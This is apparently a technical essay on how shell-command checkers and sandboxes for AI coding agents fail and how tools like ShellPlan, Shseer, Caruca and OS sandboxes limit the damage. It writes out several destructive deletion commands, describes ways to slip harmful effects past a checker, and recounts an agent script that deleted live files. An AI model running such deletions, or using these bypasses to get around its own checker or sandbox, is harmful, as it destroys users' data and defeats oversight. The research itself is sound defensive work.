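The checker answered "ask" for the running example because it couldn't find the value of `OUT`. Access to the shell's variables would solve that problem, but any checker that never answers "ask" will deny some harmless commands or allow some harmful ones.

### The proof

Suppose that the only harm is the deletion of `notes.txt`. The checker may read every program that a command runs and every file on the disk, and it may take as long as it likes, provided that it eventually answers. Now consider this command:

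```
P && rm notes.txt
```

In the command `P && rm notes.txt`, P stands for any program that leaves `notes.txt` alone. Bash runs `rm` only if P finishes and reports success, so the command is harmless if P fails or runs forever. A checker that was always right about such commands could therefore determine, for every P, whether P ever succeeds. This is a form of the halting problem, the problem of deciding whether a given program will ever finish. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no program can solve it for all programs.

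The reason is easiest to see with a script that consults the checker about itself. Suppose that a perfect checker exists as a program called `check`, which reports success if it allows a script and failure if it denies it. Somebody saves this line as `contrary.sh`:

```
if check contrary.sh; then rm notes.txt; fi
```

The script deletes the file if `check` allows it and does nothing if `check` denies it, so `check` either allows a harmful script or denies a harmless one. Refusing every script that mentions `check` does not solve the problem, because the script's author could paste in a rewritten copy of the checker's code instead, and no program can recognise every rewritten copy.

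Changing the definition of harm doesn't help. In 1953 Henry Gordon Rice extended the result to every question about what a program computes, except questions that have the same answer for all programs.

The proof assumes unlimited memory, but real computers have a fixed amount, so a checker could in theory go through every state the machine can reach. This is impractical because even one kilobyte of memory has 2⁸¹⁹² possible states, a number with 2,467 digits.

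Even a short program can be very hard to judge. Suppose `fermat.py` searches the positive whole numbers for a solution to aⁿ + bⁿ = cⁿ with n greater than 2, and reports success if it finds one. Then `python3 fermat.py && rm notes.txt` never deletes anything, because no solution exists, but mathematicians took more than 350 years to prove that.

### What the proof leaves open

A checker is sound if every command it allows is harmless, and complete if it allows every harmless command. It can be sound by denying everything or complete by allowing everything, but the proof shows that no checker can be both. A checker that can ask the user about commands it cannot classify can still be right every time it answers "allow".

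Every sound checker rejects some harmless command, and its author can improve it by allowing that command. No sound checker is therefore the best possible, so its author has to decide which commands are worth the effort of adding.

On a limited part of the language, many questions do have answers that a program can compute. Lazarek, Jung and colleagues (2025), in *From Ahead-of- to Just-in-Time and Back Again*, give examples based on the Steam accident. Steam's updater used `cd` to find its own directory, stored the result in a variable, and later deleted everything in that directory. If a user started the script by its bare name, the `cd` failed and the variable stayed empty. One of their repairs, applied to the deletion in the running example, looks like this:

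```
if [ "$(realpath "$OUT/")" != "/" ]; then rm -rf "$OUT"/*; fi
```

`realpath` prints the full path after following links. An analyser doesn't need the value of `OUT` to work out that Bash reaches the deletion only if the path isn't the root directory. If the author types `=` instead of `!=`, Bash reaches it only if the path is the root directory. ShellCheck matches patterns, so it doesn't recognise that the first version is safe or that the second is certain to go wrong. Even the first version rules out only the root directory, and `OUT` could still hold `/home/ana`.

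The same method can cover text that flows through a pipe. `lsb_release -a` prints four lines about a Linux system, beginning with `Distributor ID`, `Description`, `Release` and `Codename`. If a script pipes them into `grep '^desc'`, `grep` prints nothing because no line begins with a lower-case `desc`. An analyser can write one regular expression for the first program's possible output and another for the lines the second program keeps, then compute whether any string matches both. Unlike the halting problem, this question always has a computable answer. In the paper's example, the mistake leaves a variable unset, and a later `rm -fr` can again delete everything.

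Researchers disagree about how far static analysis of shell scripts can go. Lazarek and colleagues were replying to an earlier presentation at the same workshop, which argued that shell scripts are too dynamic to analyse in advance and that tools should analyse them while they run. They propose proving what they can beforehand and using a monitor to stop the script if it is about to break one of the remaining rules. According to *ShellFuzzer* (Felici, Pozzi and Furia, 2024), another tool, ABash, guarantees neither soundness nor completeness but still found bugs in open-source scripts. Like SaSh, it is good enough for finding faults but not for deciding which commands to allow.

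Programs like `fermat.py` are rare in coding sessions. Most of the mistakes that a checker makes have more ordinary causes.

### The same text on a different machine

A command's effect depends on much that isn't in its text. In Greenberg and Blatt's model, a shell's state includes its variables, functions and aliases, the current directory, the language settings, the background jobs and the exit status of the last command. The shell also makes system calls as part of its basic operation, and Greenberg and Blatt warn that modelling these calls faithfully can require modelling any amount of the operating system.

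Régis-Gianas and Treinen (2018), in *Parsing [S]hell*, describe a bug that came from the format of a disk. When a user removed the mail package `sendmail-base` from Debian, a maintainer script ran this line:

```
find /etc/mail -maxdepth 1 -size 0 | xargs -r rm
```

The line deletes empty files. On the Btrfs file system, a directory can also have size 0, though the line's author had probably assumed it couldn't. On one user's Btrfs disk, `rm` received the name of a directory and refused to delete it, so the user couldn't remove the package. Debian had accepted this version two months before the bug report. With `rm -r`, the line would have deleted the directory.

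A checker can reduce this uncertainty by reading the disk, and the agent's software could pass it the shell's variables. But it can't read the disk of another machine before `ssh server 'rm -r build'` runs, or the output of a program that hasn't run yet.

### Parsing that depends on execution

As described earlier, aliases can make a later line either a loop or an ordinary command, depending on whether another program succeeds. Régis-Gianas and Treinen give a variant in which the validity of the whole script depends on that program's success. To parse every such script, an analyser would have to determine in advance whether the other program succeeds, which the earlier proof showed is impossible in general.

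Régis-Gianas, Jeannerod and Treinen explain in *Morbig* (2018) that the designers of the shell language never meant it to be parsed statically, because they expected shells to alternate between reading and executing. Their parser, also called Morbig, accepts a defined subset of the language. According to Debian's *MORBIG(1)*, it carries out top-level `alias` commands, which always run, and reports an error for any inside a conditional or loop.

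Even with this restriction, Morbig parsed all 31,521 of the Debian scripts mentioned earlier, in about nine seconds on a laptop. A checker can apply the same restriction by returning "ask" where Morbig reports an error.

Oils (2016), a project developing a new shell, describes another way shells delay parsing. Bash parses a test in double brackets before it runs anything, but treats `[` as an ordinary command that interprets its arguments after expansion. If `answer` is empty, `[[ $answer = yes ]]` compares an empty string with `yes`, while `[ $answer = yes ]` becomes `[ = yes ]` and fails with an error. A checker that models the first form correctly can still be wrong about the second.

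Much of the remaining trouble with parsing is difficulty rather than impossibility. The following line is valid:

```
for do in for do in echo done; do echo $do; done
```

The first `do` is a variable name, the second is an item in the list, and the third starts the body of the loop. A parser can tell them apart by position, but the rules are long. Bash's grammar comes with about 5,000 additional lines of C code, according to Régis-Gianas and Treinen. Every checker with its own parser has to reproduce that code's behaviour or prompt the user about the parts it leaves out.

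### Shells that disagree

A perfect model of Bash gives wrong answers if another shell runs the command. This line behaves differently in Bash and Zsh:

```
OPTS="-r build"; rm $OPTS
```

If a command passes `rm` an unquoted variable containing `-r build`, Bash splits the value at the space and deletes the directory `build`. Zsh, the default shell on Macs, doesn't split unquoted variables unless the user changes a setting, so `rm` receives `-r build` as one argument and rejects it as an invalid option. The name `sh` doesn't reliably identify the shell either, since on Debian it starts Dash, a smaller shell without Bash's arrays.

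The POSIX standard doesn't settle all such differences. Greenberg and Blatt counted 70 places where its description of the shell leaves the result of a valid construct "unspecified", and 17 where it leaves the result of an invalid one "undefined". They built Smoosh, a working shell based on their mathematical model, and compared it with Bash, Dash, Zsh, OSH, mksh, ksh93 and yash. Smoosh followed the standard most closely. They also found bugs in four of the seven other shells, including Bash, and in the standard and its official tests.

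Shells also have bugs that no manual describes. Felici and colleagues tested mksh with randomly generated scripts and found eight previously unknown issues. Its maintainers confirmed seven, including two memory errors that also affected Bash. A checker built from documentation will therefore sometimes predict the wrong result. Its author can keep such errors rare by supporting only one version of one shell and comparing the checker's predictions with what that shell does.

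### Arguments that mean something different to each program

Each program interprets its own arguments after the shell has processed the command line. *An Empirical Investigation of Command-Line Customization* (2020) describes a parser that split 2.2 million alias definitions from public code repositories into commands and arguments. The parser could apply the shell's quoting rules, which are the same for every command, but it had to treat each remaining word as a separate argument because the shell language doesn't define what those words mean.

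Some programs that normally only read can also write:

| Command | Effect |
|---|---|
| `sort names.txt` | Prints the sorted lines |
| `sort names.txt -o names.txt` | Replaces the file with its sorted lines |
| `uniq names.txt` | Prints the lines without adjacent duplicates |
| `uniq names.txt short.txt` | Writes those lines to `short.txt`, replacing its contents |
| `git status` | Lists changed files, and may update Git's index, a file in `.git` |

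`uniq` writes a file here because it received a second filename, without any option or redirection. A checker needs a description of each program to catch this, and writing descriptions by hand is slow. Lazarek and colleagues propose generating them automatically. A language model reads the manual page and lists the valid options. A second tool then runs the program with many combinations of those options on test files and records what changes. For `rm -f -r` with an existing path, the result would be a rule that the path exists before the command but not afterwards, and that the exit status is 0.

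Testing helps guard against the model misreading the manual, but it covers only the situations somebody set up, and a new version of the program may behave differently. There will always be programs nobody has described, including ones the agent has just written.

### The script that followed links

In September 2026 a developer asked Claude Code for eleven repairs to software that analysed historical stock-option data. According to TechRadar, the agent was supposed to work on copies and leave the live files alone. Ten repairs went smoothly, and the last required a new mirror, a copy of the project for testing. TechRadar's *‘Do not let programs run commands on your machine’* reports that the project's own script couldn't refresh the old mirror in place, so the agent wrote a clean-up script.

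The old mirror contained 7,332 ordinary files and 614 junctions, which are Windows links that make a folder from elsewhere on the computer appear inside another. The junctions led to the live files. The clean-up script followed them and deleted 55,550 files, 48,218 of them live, in 103 seconds. It also deleted Git's stored objects and history. Git's index still listed 7,221 paths, but Git could no longer restore their contents.

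The script had a safeguard, but the accounts differ on why it failed. According to TechRadar, it protected the junction folders but not the directories below them. Centrum.cz's *AI dostala přístup k počítači*, a Czech report, says that the Python script avoided symbolic links, but a junction isn't one. All these accounts go back to a single Reddit post, which has since disappeared.

None of the reports quotes the command that started the script. If the agent had saved the script to a file, the command could have been as short as this:

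```
python clean_mirror.py
```

The command contains no deletion instruction, no path to the mirror and no mention of a link. To predict the damage, a checker would have had to read the script, trace its path through the mirror and find out which folders were junctions. It would also have had to account for the fact that Python's usual test for symbolic links, `os.path.islink`, returns false for a junction. Python 3.12 added a separate test for junctions, `os.path.isjunction`.

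All of this information was on the machine before the script ran, so the obstacle was the amount of analysis the prediction required in a second programming language, not undecidability. A cruder rule would have been more useful. The checker could ask the user to confirm any script that the agent wrote in the same session and that deletes files. It could also list the links that lead out of the target directory, of which there were 614 in this case.

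Asking the user about every script isn't practical, because developers run project code routinely. `npm test` and `pytest` run whatever code the project's files contain. Li excludes both commands from ShellPlan's formal guarantee, even when the user's policy allows them.

### Harm that no single command does

Suppose that an agent sends these two lines as separate commands:

```
mv notes.txt build/
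rm -r build
```

The first command moves a file within the project without losing any data. The second deletes a directory that the project's owner has listed as build output. A checker could reasonably allow either command on its own, but together they destroy the notes.

An analyser can find some conflicts of this kind when all the commands are in one script. In an example from Lazarek and colleagues, a script deletes a directory and then tries to read a file in it. After the first command, the analyser records that the directory no longer exists, so it can warn that the second will always fail. It could use the same method to record that `build` now contains a file that no build can recreate. The main difficulty is that the number of possible states can grow exponentially as a script branches.

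When the commands arrive separately, the checker needs a record of the earlier ones. Even a complete record of the session isn't enough if a second agent, a scheduled job or the developer runs part of the sequence. In the example, the checker could also inspect `build` just before the deletion and find that `notes.txt` is new there. This works for files, but not for harms such as a data leak in which each command takes a little more.

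### Changes after the check

A checker examines the machine before the command runs, and the machine can change in between. Programmers call the resulting mistakes time-of-check to time-of-use errors. For example, a checker may find that `build/log.txt` is an ordinary path inside the project. If another process replaces `build` with a link to another directory before Bash opens the file, Bash writes the output there instead. The gap may last only milliseconds, but it can last an hour if a person has to approve the command.

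No attacker or second process is necessary, because a command can invalidate the check by itself:

```
git pull && npm test
```

Suppose one line runs `git pull`, which downloads the latest version of the project, and then `npm test`, which runs its tests. A checker that reads the test script before the line runs reads the old version. To judge the new one, it would have to check again after `git pull` finishes and before `npm test` starts. It could do this by allowing `git pull` and asking the agent to send `npm test` separately, although the tests could still change between the second check and the run.

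### Three boundaries between approval and execution

Li defines a checker's mistake precisely enough to sort these problems by where they arise. Let *s* be the text of a command and σ the state in which it runs, consisting of the project's files, all other files and the environment variables. Eff(*s*, σ) is the set of effects that Bash produces when it runs *s* in σ without a sandbox, namely the programs it starts and the lasting changes it makes to files. A violation occurs when the checker allows *s* and Eff(*s*, σ) contains an effect that the policy prohibits. Because the definition depends on what the command does in a particular state, allowing a dangerous-looking command that fails is not a violation.

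A violation can then arise at three boundaries:

| Boundary | What goes wrong | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Parser and shell | They disagree about where a command ends or which words it contains, and the checker allows the command as a result | A checker splits `echo done; rm notes.txt` only at spaces and finds a single `echo` |
| Command and program arguments | They agree about the words, but an argument, a variable assignment or a redirection causes the prohibited effect | A checker allows `sort` as a program that only reads, and `-o` makes it write |
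| Approval and sandbox | The command runs under weaker limits than the user chose, and those limits would have prevented the effect | A checker turns the sandbox off for every command that it allows |

One violation can involve more than one boundary. If the checker in the second row also turned off a read-only sandbox, `sort -o` would cross the third boundary as well.

The third boundary is the easiest to overlook, because the checker's verdict can seem reasonable by itself. Allowing a command to run without a prompt is a different decision from allowing it to run without limits. A checker that combines the two removes the sandbox from commands that no user is asked to approve.

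Li's scheme doesn't cover everything in this section. It treats each command on its own and doesn't count reading files outside the project as a violation, so it would miss the theft of a key stored there. Li also classifies some mistakes separately, such as an allow rule that wrongly overrides a stricter one.

### What better engineering can remove

Careful design can eliminate three of the causes. A checker avoids disagreements with the shell's parser if it accepts only a small part of the language and asks for approval to run anything else. It avoids differences between shells if it supports one shell and makes sure this shell runs the command. It never weakens the sandbox if approval and confinement are separate settings.

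The other causes are different, because a better checker asks less often but can't stop asking:

| Cause | What a better checker can do | What remains |
|---|---|---|
| Missing state | Read the shell's variables, the current directory and the links on the disk | Other machines, and the results of programs that haven't run |
| Program arguments | Describe common programs and ask about the others | New programs, and new versions of old ones |
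| Scripts and interpreters | Read short scripts and analyse the simple parts | Loops and computed values, up to the undecidable cases |
| Harm over several commands | Keep a record of the session | Actions by people and programs outside the session |
| Changes after the check | Check again immediately before the command runs | Programs that open files by name later on |

The remedy for both the first and last rows is to decide later, when the missing facts are available. The operating system is better placed than the checker to do this. When the clean-up script tried to delete its first live file, Windows had already followed the junction to the file's real location.

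## Running only what was checked, and confining the rest

A checker can interpret a command differently from Bash because Bash parses the text a second time. A tool can remove this risk by starting the programs itself from the syntax tree it checked. It then needs a description of what each program does with its arguments. For programs that nobody can describe in advance, it needs a way to limit or undo any damage.

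### Starting programs without a shell

Li published ShellPlan in November 2026 to remove the second reading. Suppose that the policy allows only reading and an agent proposes this command:

```
sort names.txt | uniq
```

ShellPlan handles it in five steps:

1. It compiles the text into a plan, a tree of simple commands and operators. If the text contains a loop, a `cd` or anything else outside the supported part of Bash, it asks the user.
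2. It checks each command against the policy and a description of the program. The description of `uniq` allows at most one filename, because `uniq` writes to a second one, and the description of `sort` excludes `-o`.
3. It expands variables and wildcards itself and checks the resulting arguments again.
4. It finds each program's file and confirms that the file is outside the project.
5. It opens any redirections and starts the programs with `execve`, passing exactly the arguments that it checked.

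The third step catches problems that aren't in the command's text, such as a variable that turns out to contain `-o`. The descriptions in the second step are just as necessary. When Li tested an earlier version without them, it allowed 32 of 55 commands in which a normally harmless program writes a file or starts another program.

Git needs an extra check because a project's Git configuration can name programs for Git to run. ShellPlan lists the configuration first and starts Git only if every setting in it is on an allowlist.

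If the policy allows writing to the project, ShellPlan also checks the path of each redirection again as it opens the file. It goes down from the top of the project one directory at a time and refuses to follow links. Li tested this with a second process that kept swapping a directory for a link to a place outside the project. In 1,000 rounds, nothing was written outside the project, but 741 rounds ended in an unhandled error.

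### What Li proved

Li proved two theorems about a formal model of ShellPlan. The first is about which programs start. If ShellPlan doesn't approve a command, it starts none of the command's programs and opens none of its redirection targets. If it does approve, every process it starts directly is either a checked command from the plan or a fixed read-only test, such as the one that lists Git's configuration. No part of the command's text reaches a shell.

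The second theorem is about effects, and it applies only if ShellPlan has a description of every program in the plan. It also covers processes that those programs start. Each process must be a checked command, a fixed test or a helper that trusted configuration specifies. The only files that change are approved redirection targets, temporary files from `sort`, and Git's index. Two assumptions are necessary:

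- The environment variables, configuration and programs outside the project are trustworthy. An attacker may control every file in the project and any text that the agent reads.
- The described programs behave as described.

Li tested part of the second assumption by running the programs with 1,213 options. ShellPlan correctly identified whether each option takes the next word as its value, though an earlier version had made nine mistakes. ShellPlan is therefore unlikely to misread an argument list, but the descriptions could still omit an effect.

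Li's guarantee excludes `pytest`. When Li allowed `pytest` in a replay of recorded sessions, 44 of the 398 commands that ShellPlan admitted had prohibited effects, and all 44 were `pytest` runs.

A proof about a model also does not rule out bugs in the code. Manual reviews found eight security faults in one version of ShellPlan and six in the next. All 21 attacks that had worked earlier failed against the third version, but Li found one remaining weakness in how ShellPlan recognises Git's own directories.

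### What ShellPlan stops and what it costs

Li assembled 4,174 test attacks, each of which had a prohibited effect when Bash ran it. Under a read-only policy, ShellPlan allowed none of them. A checker that refused every command would also allow none, so how a checker treats harmless commands matters as much. ShellPlan asked for approval on 12 (7.5%) of the 161 harmless read-only commands that Li also used to test the coding agents' checkers, compared with 23% for Codex. ShellPlan allowed none of the 316 commands that weren't read-only.

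Li then gave ten language models nine tasks that contained attacks and ten harmless tasks. Nobody was available to approve commands, so "ask" had the same effect as "deny".

| | No checker | A language model as checker | ShellPlan |
|---|---|---|---|
| Successful attacks, out of 90 runs | 62 | 6 | 0 |
| Harmless tasks completed, out of 100 | 93 | 87 | 74 |
| Median checking time per task | None | 6.1 seconds | 1.3 milliseconds |

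Zero successes in 90 runs is still compatible with a true success rate of up to about 4%. Smaller models accounted for most of the lost tasks. Six frontier models completed all 60 of their harmless tasks without a checker and 56 with ShellPlan, while four smaller models fell from 33 of 40 to 18. Four of the ten harmless tasks were deliberately written to request shell features that ShellPlan doesn't support, so the loss on ordinary work should be smaller than the total suggests.

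How many steps ShellPlan admits also depends on how the agent writes its commands. In recorded sessions from SWE-bench Verified, a benchmark of real software repairs, ShellPlan admitted 343 of 456 read-only steps. In sessions from OpenHands, an open-source coding agent, it admitted none of 108, because every command began by changing to the project's directory with `cd`. Li suggests extending the compiler to track the working directory.

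The other cost of this design is that ShellPlan has to do Bash's work. In 343 comparisons on commands from SWE-bench Verified, its output matched Bash's exactly, but on another set of commands Li found a difference:

```
echo "hello world" | echo test=$(cat)
```

Bash prints `test=hello world`, while ShellPlan prints only `test=` because it doesn't connect the inner `cat` to the pipe. The output is wrong, but ShellPlan still runs only the programs it approved.

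### Describing what a program does to files

ShellPlan's descriptions determine which arguments are acceptable. A fuller description, usually called a specification, also records what the program does, so that an analyser can work out the combined effect of several commands. *ABash*, an early analyser for Bash scripts, already used a collection of such descriptions for external programs. In SaSh, the bug finder mentioned earlier, Lazarek and colleagues give each specification three parts. For `rm -r build` they are:

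| Part | Content |
|---|---|
| Before the command | `build` is a directory, or a file that the script has already read |
| After success | `build` no longer exists |
| After failure | Nothing has changed |

The condition about reading helps SaSh find data loss, since deleting a file before anything has read it may be a mistake. The last row is a simplification, because `rm -r` can fail after deleting only some of the files. Modelling every partial failure would soon give an analyser too many cases to examine.

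Narsipur, in *Statically Analyzing Shell Scripts and Their Effects in Context*, describes Shseer, an analyser from the same research group. It uses symbolic execution, which means going through a program with symbols in place of unknown values and recording what must be true of each symbol. The core of the faulty Steam updater shows how this works:

```
STEAMROOT="$(cd "${0%/*}" && echo $PWD)"
rm -fr $STEAMROOT/*
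```

`$0` holds the path that the user typed to start the script, and `${0%/*}` is the same path without its last slash and whatever follows it. Shseer analyses the two lines like this:

1. It doesn't know the value of `$0`, so it uses a symbol.
2. It considers both outcomes of `cd`. If `cd` succeeds, `STEAMROOT` is the directory that the script entered. If `cd` fails, `echo` doesn't run and `STEAMROOT` is empty.
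3. It looks up the specification of `rm` and applies the deletion to a model of the file system.
4. It uses a constraint solver, a program that determines whether a set of conditions can all be true together, to find out whether the deletion could reach the root directory. When `cd` fails, it can, so Shseer reports a bug.

To limit the number of cases, Shseer merges the two branches of an `if` afterwards. If one branch sets `x` to 10 and the other sets it to 20, the analysis continues with a single state in which the value of `x` depends on the condition.

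By default, Shseer considers any environment in which the script might run, but it can also start from the current one. Starting from the current environment would suit a checker, which only has to analyze a command for the machine and directory where it is about to run.

Narsipur calls Shseer a bug finder, not a verification tool. Like SaSh, it can assume that a program without a specification does not modify the file system. It also assumes that the variables in `rm $1 $2` never contain an option such as `-r`. A pre-execution checker has to prompt the user in both cases.

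SaSh has since found 70 new bugs in 44 open-source projects, including PyTorch and Kubernetes, and maintainers had accepted 27 fixes by the time Lazarek and colleagues wrote their paper. It missed one documented bug, in Debian's `debootstrap`. When a user asked that script for a list of packages, it provided the list but then deleted the directory the user had named. SaSh doesn't normally report the deletion of a user-supplied directory, because this is often what the user wants.

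### Deriving specifications by running programs

*Caruca* (Lamprou, Lazarek and colleagues, 2025) reports that two graduate students needed 80 person-hours just to record the argument types of 120 commands. The paper's tool, also called Caruca, implements the proposal from the previous section by using a language model to extract the options from the manual page and test runs to supply the rest.

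Caruca runs a program with combinations of up to four options, on paths that lead to a file, an empty directory, a non-empty directory, or nothing. For `rm` alone, this gives about 8.7 million combinations. Caruca records the program's system calls (its requests to the operating system) and compares the file system before and after each run.

Lamprou and colleagues compared Caruca's specifications for 60 commands with handwritten ones and found that 59 of Caruca's were correct. The exception was `git`, because Caruca can't yet create a repository to test it on. With Caruca's specifications, Shseer found the bugs in all 12 of its test scripts. Caruca finished 80 of 120 commands within an hour each. With a limit of two options it finished 103, though the image converter `convert` would still have taken about 99 hours.

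Caruca's tests reportedly cover 97.78% of 666,468 commands from shell scripts on GitHub, if two commands count as equivalent even when their filenames, numbers, text and argument counts differ. Coverage is only 18% if differences in text and argument count matter. The higher figure is fair for `echo`, which prints any text in the same way, but not for `xargs`, where the text can name another program to run.

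Covering common usage also matters less for a checker than for a bug finder, because an attacker can choose a rare option. Caruca doesn't vary environment variables or create symbolic links, and both can change where a program writes. Its specifications could save a checker's author a lot of work, but the checker should still ask about any option or kind of argument the specifications don't cover.

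### Limits that the operating system enforces

No specification exists for a script that the agent just wrote. A sandbox can still confine it, because the operating system handles each request to open or delete a file when the program makes it. The same limits apply whether the request comes from `rm`, a Python script or a program that the script starts.

Claude Code and Codex both have sandboxes for shell commands. Anthropic and OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* document these defaults:

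| | Claude Code | Codex on the user's machine |
|---|---|---|
| Is the sandbox on? | No, the user has to turn it on | Yes |
| Where can commands write? | The working directory and a temporary directory | The same, except for `.git` and two configuration directories |
| Can they use the network? | Only to reach approved domains | No |
| Does it work on Windows? | Only in WSL2, a Linux environment for Windows | Yes |

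On Linux, both use a program called bubblewrap, which can give a command its own view of the file system with most directories read-only. Claude Code also cuts the command off from the network, except for a proxy that checks each domain.

In the running example, the dangerous part that runs without `sudo` is `rm -rf "$OUT"/*`. Suppose `OUT` is empty and the agent is working in `/home/ana/site`. `rm` still receives every top-level directory, but in a sandbox it can delete only what it has permission to write. It deletes the source files of Ana's project, because the agent needs write access to them to do its work, but leaves her photos and system settings intact.

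Li's measurements show the same gap. With changes to the project allowed, Codex's sandbox prevented all 968 attacks in one collection from changing files outside the project, and blocked all eight attempts to alter `.git`. It permitted all 20 changes to ordinary project files, as intended. Claude Code protects a smaller part of `.git`, mainly the hooks and configuration, so a sandboxed command can make a commit but could also damage the project's history.

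By default, Claude Code's sandbox lets commands read almost the whole disk, including credential files. University of Vermont's *Claude Code Permissions & Sandboxing* (2026) says the most common mistake is believing that the sandbox restricts everything Claude reads. The agent's built-in tool for reading files doesn't go through the sandbox, so the user also needs permission rules for it.

Blocking access to credential files breaks the programs that need them. Claude Code offers an alternative called masking. On Linux, the command reads a placeholder instead of the real token, and the proxy replaces the placeholder with the token in requests to approved servers. A program can then log in to GitHub, for example, without the token appearing in its output or reaching the model.

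### Keeping approval apart from confinement

OpenAI describes Codex's protection as two layers. The sandbox mode determines what a command can do, and the approval policy determines when Codex has to ask for approval. But a single "allow" rule can change both layers, because OpenAI defines "allow" as running the command outside the sandbox without a prompt.

Li measured the effect with the sandbox in read-only mode. Inside the sandbox, none of the 55 commands that misuse normally harmless programs changed any files. After Li added rules that allowed those programs, 39 of the 55 matched a rule that turned the sandbox off. In ten live trials with such rules, all ten commands had the prohibited effect and no sandbox started. A user who wrote the rules only to avoid prompts for reading files would have less protection than a user with no rules.

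Approving a command should never turn off the sandbox, because the sandbox is meant to contain commands that the checker, or the person answering its prompt, wrongly allows.

Claude Code normally keeps an allowed command in the sandbox. If the command fails there, Claude may retry it outside, and Anthropic warns that an allow rule for the command also approves the retry. Users can prevent these retries by setting `allowUnsandboxedCommands` to false. Unless they also set `failIfUnavailable` to true, Claude Code runs commands without a sandbox if the sandbox can't start.

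Some legitimate programs need more access than the sandbox gives them. Allowing the one directory or domain that a program needs is safer than exempting the program from the sandbox. An exempt program has all of the user's rights, and if it reads instructions from a project file, the agent can edit that file before running the program.

Sandboxing a command can reasonably affect whether it needs approval, as long as approval doesn't change the sandbox. Claude Code can run most sandboxed commands without a prompt because the sandbox limits the damage they can do.

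### Previewing changes and undoing them

A tool can protect the project files that an agent is allowed to change by keeping both the old and the new versions. An overlay file system does this by keeping the original files in a read-only layer and recording the command's writes and deletions in a second layer on top. The two layers appear to the command as one file system. Afterwards the tool can list the changes in the second layer, and the user can keep or discard them.

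For `rm -rf "$OUT"/*`, the user would see a list of deleted files instead of a variable with an unknown value. Reviewing that list is much easier than predicting it. Caruca uses the same method to find which files a program changes.

Gyawali, Kallas and colleagues (2025), in *NaSh*, propose a shell that accepts requests in ordinary language and lets users reverse its mistakes. They point out three drawbacks of overlays:

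- Other programs can't see the changes until the user keeps them, and then the user can no longer discard them.
- Each command adds a layer, and opening a file gets slower as the system searches more layers.
- Changes to special files, such as system settings in `/proc`, have no effect.

Their alternative is an inverse overlay, which makes each change to the real files immediately, so other programs can use the new files, and saves the old version. The user can restore the old files for as long as there is disk space to store them.

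An inverse overlay would help with the two commands in the previous section that moved `notes.txt` into `build` and then deleted `build`. Each command looks harmless, so a user might well keep the result of both after a preview. The user could still recover the notes after discovering the loss.

Undoing a command can cause problems for later commands that depended on it. If one command installs a package and the next installs a second package that needs it, undoing only the first command breaks the second package. Gyawali and colleagues would detect two commands that changed the same file, but they consider conflicts like this one hard to find. NaSh is also only a design so far, without measurements of its speed or reliability.

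Neither kind of overlay can take back data that a command has sent to another machine. NaSh therefore blocks network access unless the user permits it.

The following table shows how far each response handles the causes in the previous section, together with leaks of secrets:

| Cause | Running the checked plan | Specifications | Sandbox | Overlay or undo |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| The checker and the shell read the text differently | Removes the cause | No help | Limits the damage to permitted directories | Reverses changes to files |
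| Variables and links are unknown during the check | Checks again after expansion | Cover many possible values at once | Applies to the file's real location | Shows which files changed |
| Program arguments have unexpected effects | Needs specifications | Main remedy for known programs | Limits the damage | Reverses changes to files |
| A script or interpreter does the work | Has to ask or rely on trust | Little help with new scripts | Main remedy outside the workspace | Main remedy inside the workspace |
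| Several commands cause harm together | No help | Help if the analyser remembers earlier commands | Limits the damage | Main remedy, if the old versions still exist |
| Files change after the check | Checks redirections again on opening | No help | Applies when the program opens the file | Reverses changes to files |
| A command sends secrets elsewhere | Outside ShellPlan's scope | Can identify which files a program reads | Main remedy, if it restricts reading and the network | No help |

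## Testing a checker

Sandboxes and overlays limit the damage when a checker wrongly allows a command. To measure how often this happens, the checker's author has to test it on commands already labeled dangerous or harmless.

### The procedure

1. Write down the policy. Without one, nobody can say whether allowing `rm -r build` is a mistake.
2. Collect dangerous and harmless commands, and label them according to the policy.
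3. Put related commands into groups, and place each group entirely in the tuning set or entirely in the test set.
4. Adjust the checker's rules and thresholds on the tuning set.
5. Run the finished checker on the test set, and record each verdict and how long it took.
6. Run the commands in an isolated container, and compare their effects with the verdicts.

The third step matters because many commands in public collections are near-copies of each other. For example, a rule written for `find . -name '*.log' -delete` in the tuning set will also catch `find . -name '*.tmp' -delete` in the test set, but this doesn't show that the checker can handle unfamiliar commands.

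Liu and colleagues grouped CARE's 1,862 commands by template to keep variants of the same attack together, then used 1,313 commands for tuning and kept 549 for the main test. For a separate test, they divided GTFOBins entries by program, so that no program appeared in both the test entries and the ones they used to write rules.

The fifth step gives the detection rate, the false-positive rate and the delay. The first two depend on how "ask" verdicts are counted. Liu and colleagues count a WARN as a stopped command when CARE runs without its language model. This is reasonable if nobody is available to answer, but it overstates the protection if a person approves nearly every prompt. A report on a checker should therefore give separate figures for "ask" and "deny".

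### Where test commands come from

Three public collections supply most of the commands in CARE's main test, and their creators made all three for other purposes.

Atomic Red Team is a library of small tests that imitate attackers' techniques, organised by ATT&CK category. Its main purpose, according to Red Canary's *Atomic Red Team* (2024), is to find out whether monitoring tools record the evidence needed to recognise an attack. A test can do this without harming anything. For example, one of the library's file-deletion tests, described in *T1070.004*, creates a file in a temporary directory and then deletes it. If a test set labels this deletion "dangerous", a checker that sensibly allows it gets a lower detection rate.

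*RedCode* (Guo, Liu and colleagues, 2024) tests whether coding agents refuse to run risky code. It describes 25 risky scenarios in Python, with 30 variants of each. GPT-4 translated the variants of 20 scenarios into Bash, so the 600 Bash test cases cover only 20 basic ideas. The translations keep the Python variable names, so they may not resemble what an agent would type. Some of the web addresses contain words such as "malicious", which makes them easier to recognise than real malicious addresses. When Guo and colleagues tried addresses made of random characters, agents refused less often.

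Lin, Wang and colleagues (2018) hired freelancers to collect one-line commands from forums, tutorials and course pages, each with an English description. They built this dataset, *NL2Bash*, to train programs that translate English into Bash. Its commands can be used as harmless examples when testing a checker, but this assumes they are harmless, because nobody assessed their safety.

The cleaned version of NL2Bash has 9,305 pairs of commands and descriptions. Lin and colleagues left out commands with redirections, variable assignments, loops or functions, and removed `sudo` from the start of the others. These are among the features that most often cause false alarms, so a checker would raise fewer false alarms on this version than in practice. The program `find` appears 6,268 times because the first round of collection was limited to it.

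Liu and colleagues avoided some of these problems. They sampled from 12,607 pairs, nearly the whole collection before cleaning, and balanced the sample by program. They also added 30 common developer commands, such as `pip install -r requirements.txt`.

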